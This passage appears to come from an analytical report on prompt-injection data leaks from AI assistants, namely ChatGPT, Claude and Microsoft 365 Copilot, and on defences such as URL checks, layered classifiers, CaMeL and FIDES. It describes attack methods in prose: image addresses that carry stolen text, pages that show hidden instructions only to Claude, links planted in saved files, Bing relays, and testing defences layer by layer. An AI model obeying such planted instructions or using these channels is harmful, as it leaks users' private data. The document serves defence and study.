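Even without these extra measures, the exact-match rule greatly reduces how much an attacker can steal with each request. A single request could previously carry a whole paragraph of an email, which would now take hundreds of requests, one for each character. Imperva had already concluded from the 2024 version that stealing large amounts of data unnoticed had become much harder. Providers can also check their logs for long series of requests to nearly identical addresses, which are unusual.

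### A similar rule in Claude

Anthropic uses a related rule for Claude's tool for reading web pages. The tool may open only exact addresses that the user has entered or that Claude's search tool has returned (Willison, 2026). When Anthropic released the tool to developers in September 2025, it still advised them to use it only in trusted environments or with non-sensitive data (Willison, 2025).

The rule had an exception that let Claude follow links on pages it had already opened. In July 2026 Willison reported that Ayush Paul had used this to extract a user's name, home city and employer. Paul's website told Claude to find the user's profile by following links letter by letter. Each page led to a new set of links, and the ones Claude followed spelled out these details. The site showed these instructions only to visitors that identified themselves as Claude, so a person checking the page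 would not have seen them.

This gap was worse than the one in OpenAI's rule because Paul's server could generate new addresses on demand, without waiting for a crawler, so a ban on repeat visits would have had no effect. Anthropic closed the gap by stopping the tool from following links on pages it has fetched. It paid no reward, saying its own staff had already found the problem. The fix makes Claude less convenient for research, since it can open a source linked in an article only if the user enters the address or a search returns it. An attacker can still try to get a set of pages into the search results, so roughly the same leak remains as with OpenAI's list.

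### Products that never run the check

Rehberger's last concern about OpenAI's rule is that some of the company's own developers may not know it exists. The phone and desktop apps were earlier examples of this problem. Another became public in January 2026, when Red Hot Cyber's *OpenAI API Logs Vulnerability Exposed* (2026) described PromptArmor's research on the page where developers read the logs of apps they have built with OpenAI's models. That page displayed Markdown images, so even if an app correctly withheld a malicious answer from its user, the data would still leak when a developer opened the log to investigate.

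In March 2026 OpenAI said that the check, which it now calls Safe Url, is used in ChatGPT, in the Atlas browser for pages and bookmarks, and in Deep Research for searches and pages. Small programs that ChatGPT creates for users run in a sandbox that detects unexpected outside connections and asks the user for permission.

A provider can run the check on its own servers, as Rehberger recommended in 2023, to reduce the risk that developers leave it out of a new app. For images, the server has to check each address before it sends the answer to the app.

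The same precaution is needed when an assistant sends its answers through a messaging app that fetches link previews. PromptArmor found that the AI agent OpenClaw was exposed by default when used through Telegram. The app fetches the preview without using the agent's browsing tool, so a check built into that tool would not stop the leak.

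## How long server-side patches hold

Microsoft had fixed EchoLeak by June 2025. In the summer of 2026, the same research team, now called Cato AI Labs, extracted data from Microsoft 365 Copilot in three new ways. Cato published the attacks as ReLeak on 3 December 2026, after Microsoft had fixed all three.

### Three new ways out of Copilot

Like EchoLeak, each attack begins with an outsider's email, which Copilot retrieves when an employee asks an ordinary work question. The employee does not have to open the email, click a link or approve anything. *ReLeak: furto di dati tramite Microsoft 365 Copilot* (Colantuoni, 2026) reports that Copilot rejected direct commands, but that instructions that looked like legitimate requests got past Microsoft's XPIA defences and Copilot followed them.

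In the first attack, Copilot wrote a Markdown image into its answer, with confidential text in the image's address. The browser loaded the image automatically through Bing, and Bing's servers passed the text on to the attacker's server.

The second attack used Copilot's ability to write Word, Excel, PowerPoint and PDF files and save them in OneDrive or SharePoint. Suppose Ana asks for help with the party, and the injected instructions make Copilot save a planning document containing a link to pictures.example with the date in its address. Even if Ana never opens the document, Microsoft's servers request the link when they process stored files in the background, and the request delivers the date. Antipov (2026) reports in *Письмо даже не нужно открывать* that in Cato's tests this happened one to eight minutes after the conversation had ended. Cleaning the chat answer would not have helped,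 because the link was in a file. A Content Security Policy would not have helped either, because only browsers enforce it and the request came from a server.

The third attack made Copilot's code interpreter, which runs programs in an isolated environment, send data directly to an outside server.

Cato reported the three flaws between 29 July and 20 August 2026. Faisal (2026), in *An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief*, gives the date of each fix:

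| Route | CVE number | Fixed in 2026 | Days after Cato's report |
|---|---|---|---|
| Code interpreter | CVE-2026-78501 | 17 September | 28 to 50 |
| Background processing of files | CVE-2026-124132 | 11 November | 83 to 105 |
| Bing image relay | CVE-2026-124115 | 15 November | 87 to 109 |

The last column gives ranges because the accounts do not match each flaw to a reporting date. Even the slowest repair was faster than EchoLeak's, which took about four months.

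Microsoft rated the code-interpreter flaw critical and raised its score from 7.4 to 8.6 out of 10. On the day of publication, the CVE numbers of the other two flaws were reserved but had no public records yet. Cato knew of no affected customers.

### Was it the same hole in Bing?

Copilot's pages had long permitted images from Bing. The list of image hosts that Ravia published in 2025 included `bing.com` and the wildcard `*.bing.com`, although EchoLeak went through Teams. SearchLeak used Bing's similar-image search as a relay, and Microsoft published its record of the flaw on 4 June 2026. Cato reported its own Bing relay between 55 and 77 days later.

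It is unclear whether both attacks used the same Bing service. Antipov calls the two channels similar, and neither Antipov nor Faisal names the service ReLeak used.

If ReLeak used the same relay as SearchLeak, Microsoft had either repaired the relay incompletely or stopped SearchLeak at one of its other two weak points. SearchLeak also needed a specially made link and an image that loaded before Copilot had cleaned the answer, so fixing either would have ended that attack but left the relay working. ReLeak started from an email and did not need the link. If ReLeak used a different service as its relay, Microsoft may have closed the first relay properly but missed a second one on the same permitted site.

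In both cases, the browser would have blocked the image if Copilot's policy had no longer permitted any Bing host. A shorter list of permitted hosts might not have been enough. In 2023 Microsoft limited Bing Chat to four named Bing hosts, far fewer than a wildcard allows, but one was `www.bing.com`, the main site with most of Bing's services. It would be safer to use a separate host that serves only stored pictures and never contacts an address from the request.

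Microsoft fixed the Bing flaw last of the three, though it had dealt with a similar one earlier that year. It has not said why. Other products may depend on the Bing service, so its owners may not have been able to simply switch it off.

### The record since 2024

Researchers have found many other ways to get data out of Microsoft's assistants. In 2024 Johann Rehberger and others combined prompt injection with "ASCII smuggling", which hides stolen text in a link as invisible characters. The OECD's *Microsoft Copilot Vulnerability Exposed Sensitive Data* (2024) notes that Microsoft patched the flaws without disclosing how. The Next Web lists SearchLeak with EchoLeak and Reprompt, an attack on the consumer version of Copilot that Varonis published in January 2026.

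Varonis attacked the consumer version of Copilot again that summer. Its *CoSnitch* describes a one-click attack that exploited weak points the researchers got Copilot to reveal, a method they call "meta-hacking". The attack used malicious links and instructions planted in Copilot's memory, according to TechRadar's *Experts manage to hack Microsoft Copilot by continually asking it questions*. Microsoft fixed the flaw, CVE-2026-24301, on its own servers.

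| Made public | Attack | What the victim did | Weakness it relied on |
|---|---|---|---|
| August 2024 | ASCII smuggling | Clicked a link in the answer | Invisible characters in the link |
| June 2025 | EchoLeak | Asked a question | Relay in Teams |
| October 2025 | Logue's diagram attack | Asked for a summary, then clicked | Link inside a Mermaid diagram |
| January 2026 | Reprompt | Clicked a link to Copilot | Instructions in the link |
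| May 2026 | Copilot Cowork leak | Opened a message from the agent | Outside images in emails |
| June 2026 | SearchLeak | Clicked a link to Copilot | Late sanitisation and a relay in Bing |
| August 2026 | CoSnitch | Clicked a link | Links and planted memories |
| December 2026 | ReLeak | Asked a question | Relay in Bing, file processing, code interpreter |

Readers cannot use this list to rank Copilot against its competitors. Researchers concentrate on products that large companies use, and every published attack gives the next team a starting point. The list also omits flaws that nobody reported.

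The individual repairs seem to have held, since none of these accounts describes an earlier attack working again unchanged after Microsoft had declared it fixed. But new attacks kept combining text that Copilot wrongly treated as a proper request with some part of the product that would contact an outside address. Faisal quotes Cato's verdict that "too little progress has been made".

Several entries depend on features that Microsoft added to its assistants, such as drawing diagrams, writing files and running code. The Copilot Cowork leak that Willison (2026) recorded depended on the agent's ability to email its own user. A patch can keep protecting a product as it grows only if somebody applies the same rule to each new feature before release.

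### A repair that customers cannot inspect

On 17 September 2026, the day it fixed the code-interpreter flaw, Microsoft announced repairs to 18 flaws in Azure, Microsoft 365 Copilot and other cloud services. Seven had the maximum severity score of 10.0, and customers had nothing to install, according to *Microsoft、Azure・Copilotなど18件の脆弱性を修正* (三村, 2026). If the flaws had been in programs on people's own computers, many companies would have taken weeks to install the updates and some would never have installed them.

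Server-side repair also denies attackers a common shortcut. When a company patches an installed program, attackers can compare the old and new versions to find the flaw, then attack everyone who has not updated. With an online service, they have no program files to compare, and no customer is still running the old version.

Customers cannot inspect a server-side patch, so they do not know which step of an attack it blocks or whether it covers similar cases. They also cannot tell if a later update undoes it, and they cannot stay on a version they have tested. Repeating the published attack gives limited reassurance, because the attack fails if any one of its steps is blocked, even if the others still work.

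Customers also don't know about a flaw while it is being repaired. The Bing relay remained open for about three months after Cato reported it. An administrator who knew about it might have kept outside email away from Copilot until it was fixed. Telling customers would have alerted attackers too, so Microsoft and Cato were probably right to stay silent, but this left customers with a risk they could not assess.

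The case for publishing details is much stronger once every customer has the fix. Companies often keep quiet about a flaw to protect people who have not updated, but a cloud service has no such users. Microsoft could say whether it changed the classifier, the sanitiser or the relay without revealing any code. The strongest counterargument is that a precise description of one closed relay shows attackers what kind of service to look for next. That risk is real on a site as large as Bing, though the researchers' reports already reveal most of this information.

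Anyone with an account can inspect one part of the defence, the list of permitted image hosts, because the server sends the Content Security Policy to every browser that opens the page. A company's security staff could check the list every month and ask Microsoft about any wildcard, but they could not tell from it which permitted hosts contain a relay.

### Microsoft's layers

Microsoft does not expect any single defence to hold. Its July 2025 account, *How Microsoft defends against indirect prompt injection attacks*, describes several layers. Carefully written system prompts and Spotlighting, which marks outside text as untrusted, make it harder for planted text to steer the model. Prompt Shields is designed to detect planted text. Access permissions, requests for the user's approval, and blocks on known exfiltration methods limit the damage if an injection succeeds.

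Spotlighting and Prompt Shields are this system's probabilistic defences. A language model's output is partly random, so no number of failed attacks proves that the next one will fail. The blocks on exfiltration methods are deterministic.

Classifiers and fixed rules fail differently. A classifier that misses 10% of attacks will keep missing some, and retraining may reduce that share without bringing it to zero. A fixed rule stops every attack it covers, but once someone finds a gap, attacks that use it can work every time. For example, Copilot's link redaction consistently missed reference-style links. Engineers can close a gap like this completely.

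A deterministic guarantee also covers only what its rule covers. A rule about images in answers doesn't protect against links in saved files. The software that enforces the rule can have faults too. Microsoft promised in its documentation, as Antipov points out, that no network traffic could enter or leave the code interpreter's environment, but Cato got data out of it.

### What three layers are worth

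Suppose an attack has to pass three layers and each lets through 10% of attempts. If the layers are independent, the share that passes all three is

0.1 × 0.1 × 0.1 = 0.001, or 0.1%

An attacker needs an average of 1 ÷ 0.001 = 1,000 attempts to succeed once. A fourth layer of the same quality would raise that to 10,000.

Now suppose the attacker can test each layer separately. It takes 10 attempts on average to find something that passes the first layer, 10 more for the second and 10 for the third, so

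10 + 10 + 10 = 30

attempts are enough if the attacker can combine the three results in one email. A fourth layer then adds only 10 attempts.

Attackers with their own Copilot account can often tell which defences a test email has passed. If Copilot's answer reflects something in the email, the text has passed the classifier and Copilot has retrieved it. If a link appears, it has passed the sanitiser. The browser's developer tools show any image that the Content Security Policy blocks. Aim Labs found EchoLeak by getting past one defence at a time.

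Combining bypasses for several defences can be harder than finding each one separately, because a sentence mild enough to pass a classifier may be too mild to steer the model, as the contestants in LLMail-Inject discovered. But a link format or a relay works with almost any wording, so an attacker who has found one can keep it and revise only the text.

Real layers are also not independent. A request that reads like ordinary office work tends to pass a classifier, a second model acting as judge, and a person asked for approval, all for the same reason. Suppose the first layer still passes 10%, but each later layer passes half of what reaches it:

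0.1 × 0.5 × 0.5 = 0.025, or 2.5%

An attacker then needs forty attempts on average, even without testing each check separately. Three checks on an email's wording therefore protect less well than one check on its wording, one on the links in the answer and one on where the server connects.

Cato's researchers used AI agents for much of this work, directing them to write test cases, analyse Copilot's refusals and adjust the next tests. Agents that run day and night can easily make either 30 or 1,000 attempts. The difference matters more to a provider trying to detect an attack, because 30 test emails in a paying customer's account look much like normal use.

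### Changing the design

According to Cato, the underlying fault is that Copilot could not reliably tell untrusted content from legitimate instructions. On this view, better classifiers and more patches would not fix this, and the assistant should be built so that a planted instruction has no effect even when the model treats it as legitimate.

In March 2025 Edoardo Debenedetti and colleagues, most of them at Google and ETH Zurich, proposed such a design, called CaMeL, in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design*. It uses two language models. The privileged model receives the user's request but never the content of any email or web page. The quarantined model processes that content but cannot use tools.

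Suppose Ana asks the assistant to send the date of the party to the caterer in her address book. CaMeL would handle this in four steps:

1. The privileged model turns Ana's request into a short program: find the email about the party, extract the date, look up the caterer and send the date.
2. An interpreter, the software that runs the program, searches Ana's mail and gives the results to the quarantined model.
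3. The quarantined model returns a date. The interpreter labels this value with its origin and with the people who may read it.
4. Before sending the email, the interpreter checks the labels against a written security policy. It sends the message, refuses, or asks Ana.

If the outsider's newsletter is among the search results, its hidden instruction can reach only the quarantined model. That model might return a wrong date, but it cannot add a step to the program or choose another recipient.

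The researchers claim provable security in the sense that untrusted content cannot change which steps the program contains, and a value cannot reach a tool against the policy. They do not claim that the answers are correct, so the caterer could still receive a false date. Some information can also leak through side channels, for example if the number of times the program repeats a web request depends on private data.

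In the revised version of the paper, CaMeL completed 77% of the tasks in AgentDojo with this guarantee, compared with 84% for an undefended system. It also used nearly three times as many tokens, and somebody has to write a policy for every tool. It does worst on requests like "do what my colleague's email asks", because nobody can write the program before reading the email.

### FIDES and the cost of labels

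Microsoft's researchers published a related design, FIDES, in May 2025. Manuel Costa, Boris Köpf and colleagues describe it in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*. FIDES has one main model that can still plan as it goes, and the software around it attaches two labels to every piece of data. One label records whether the source is trusted, and the other who may read the data. When the model has several pieces in front of it, the combination gets the stricter label of each kind. For Ana's original question about the party, it might look like this:

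| Data | Trusted? | Who may read it |
|---|---|---|
| Ana's question | Yes | Company staff |
| Her colleague's email | Yes | Company staff |
| The outsider's newsletter | No | Anyone |
| All three together | No | Company staff |

Anything the model writes from this combination inherits the labels in the last row. The software can then refuse to put the text in an image address at pictures.example, because the site's owner is not on the company's staff. It can do this without recognising the injection. The labels capture what Ravia calls a scope violation, in which an outside email draws on inside data.

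Applying the labels strictly would make the assistant nearly useless, because reading one newsletter would make the whole conversation untrusted and block every important action. FIDES therefore puts untrusted text into a variable, a named container that the main model can pass to a tool without seeing the contents. If the main model needs a fact from the text, it can query a separate model whose answer is restricted to a set form, such as yes or no.

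Costa and colleagues also tested FIDES on AgentDojo and report that it can complete a broad range of tasks with security guarantees. How much capability it loses depends on the task. It loses none when forwarding a report, since the assistant need not read it, and sorting messages into two folders needs only restricted answers. It loses the most when following instructions in a document, because the contents determine what to do next, so the software must refuse or ask the user.

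Labels would not have removed every weakness behind ReLeak. The policy must still define which destinations count as outside the company. If it treated Bing as a safe Microsoft address, it would allow confidential text to go to Bing, and from there the text could reach the attacker. The labels would also have to stay attached to the text in saved files, which a different team's software processes later.

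### What had reached users by 2026

Google has put parts of this approach into Chrome. *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome*, which it published in December 2025, describes the protection for the browser's Gemini agent. A second model checks each action the agent proposes and can veto it. This model receives a description of the action but none of the web page's text, a design that Google says drew partly on CaMeL. Chrome also restricts which sites the agent may read from and act on during a task.

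These defences offer less protection than CaMeL. The second model is still a probabilistic defence because it relies on judgement, although an attacker cannot address it directly. The limits on sites are closer to a fixed rule, but they depend on deciding which sites a task requires, and a permitted site may contain a form or a relay that an attacker could use.

In July 2025, Microsoft described FIDES as research. A year later, an outsider's email could still make Copilot send internal data through an image, a saved file and a program. Microsoft may have adopted parts of FIDES by then, but it did not yet enforce FIDES's labels on those three routes.
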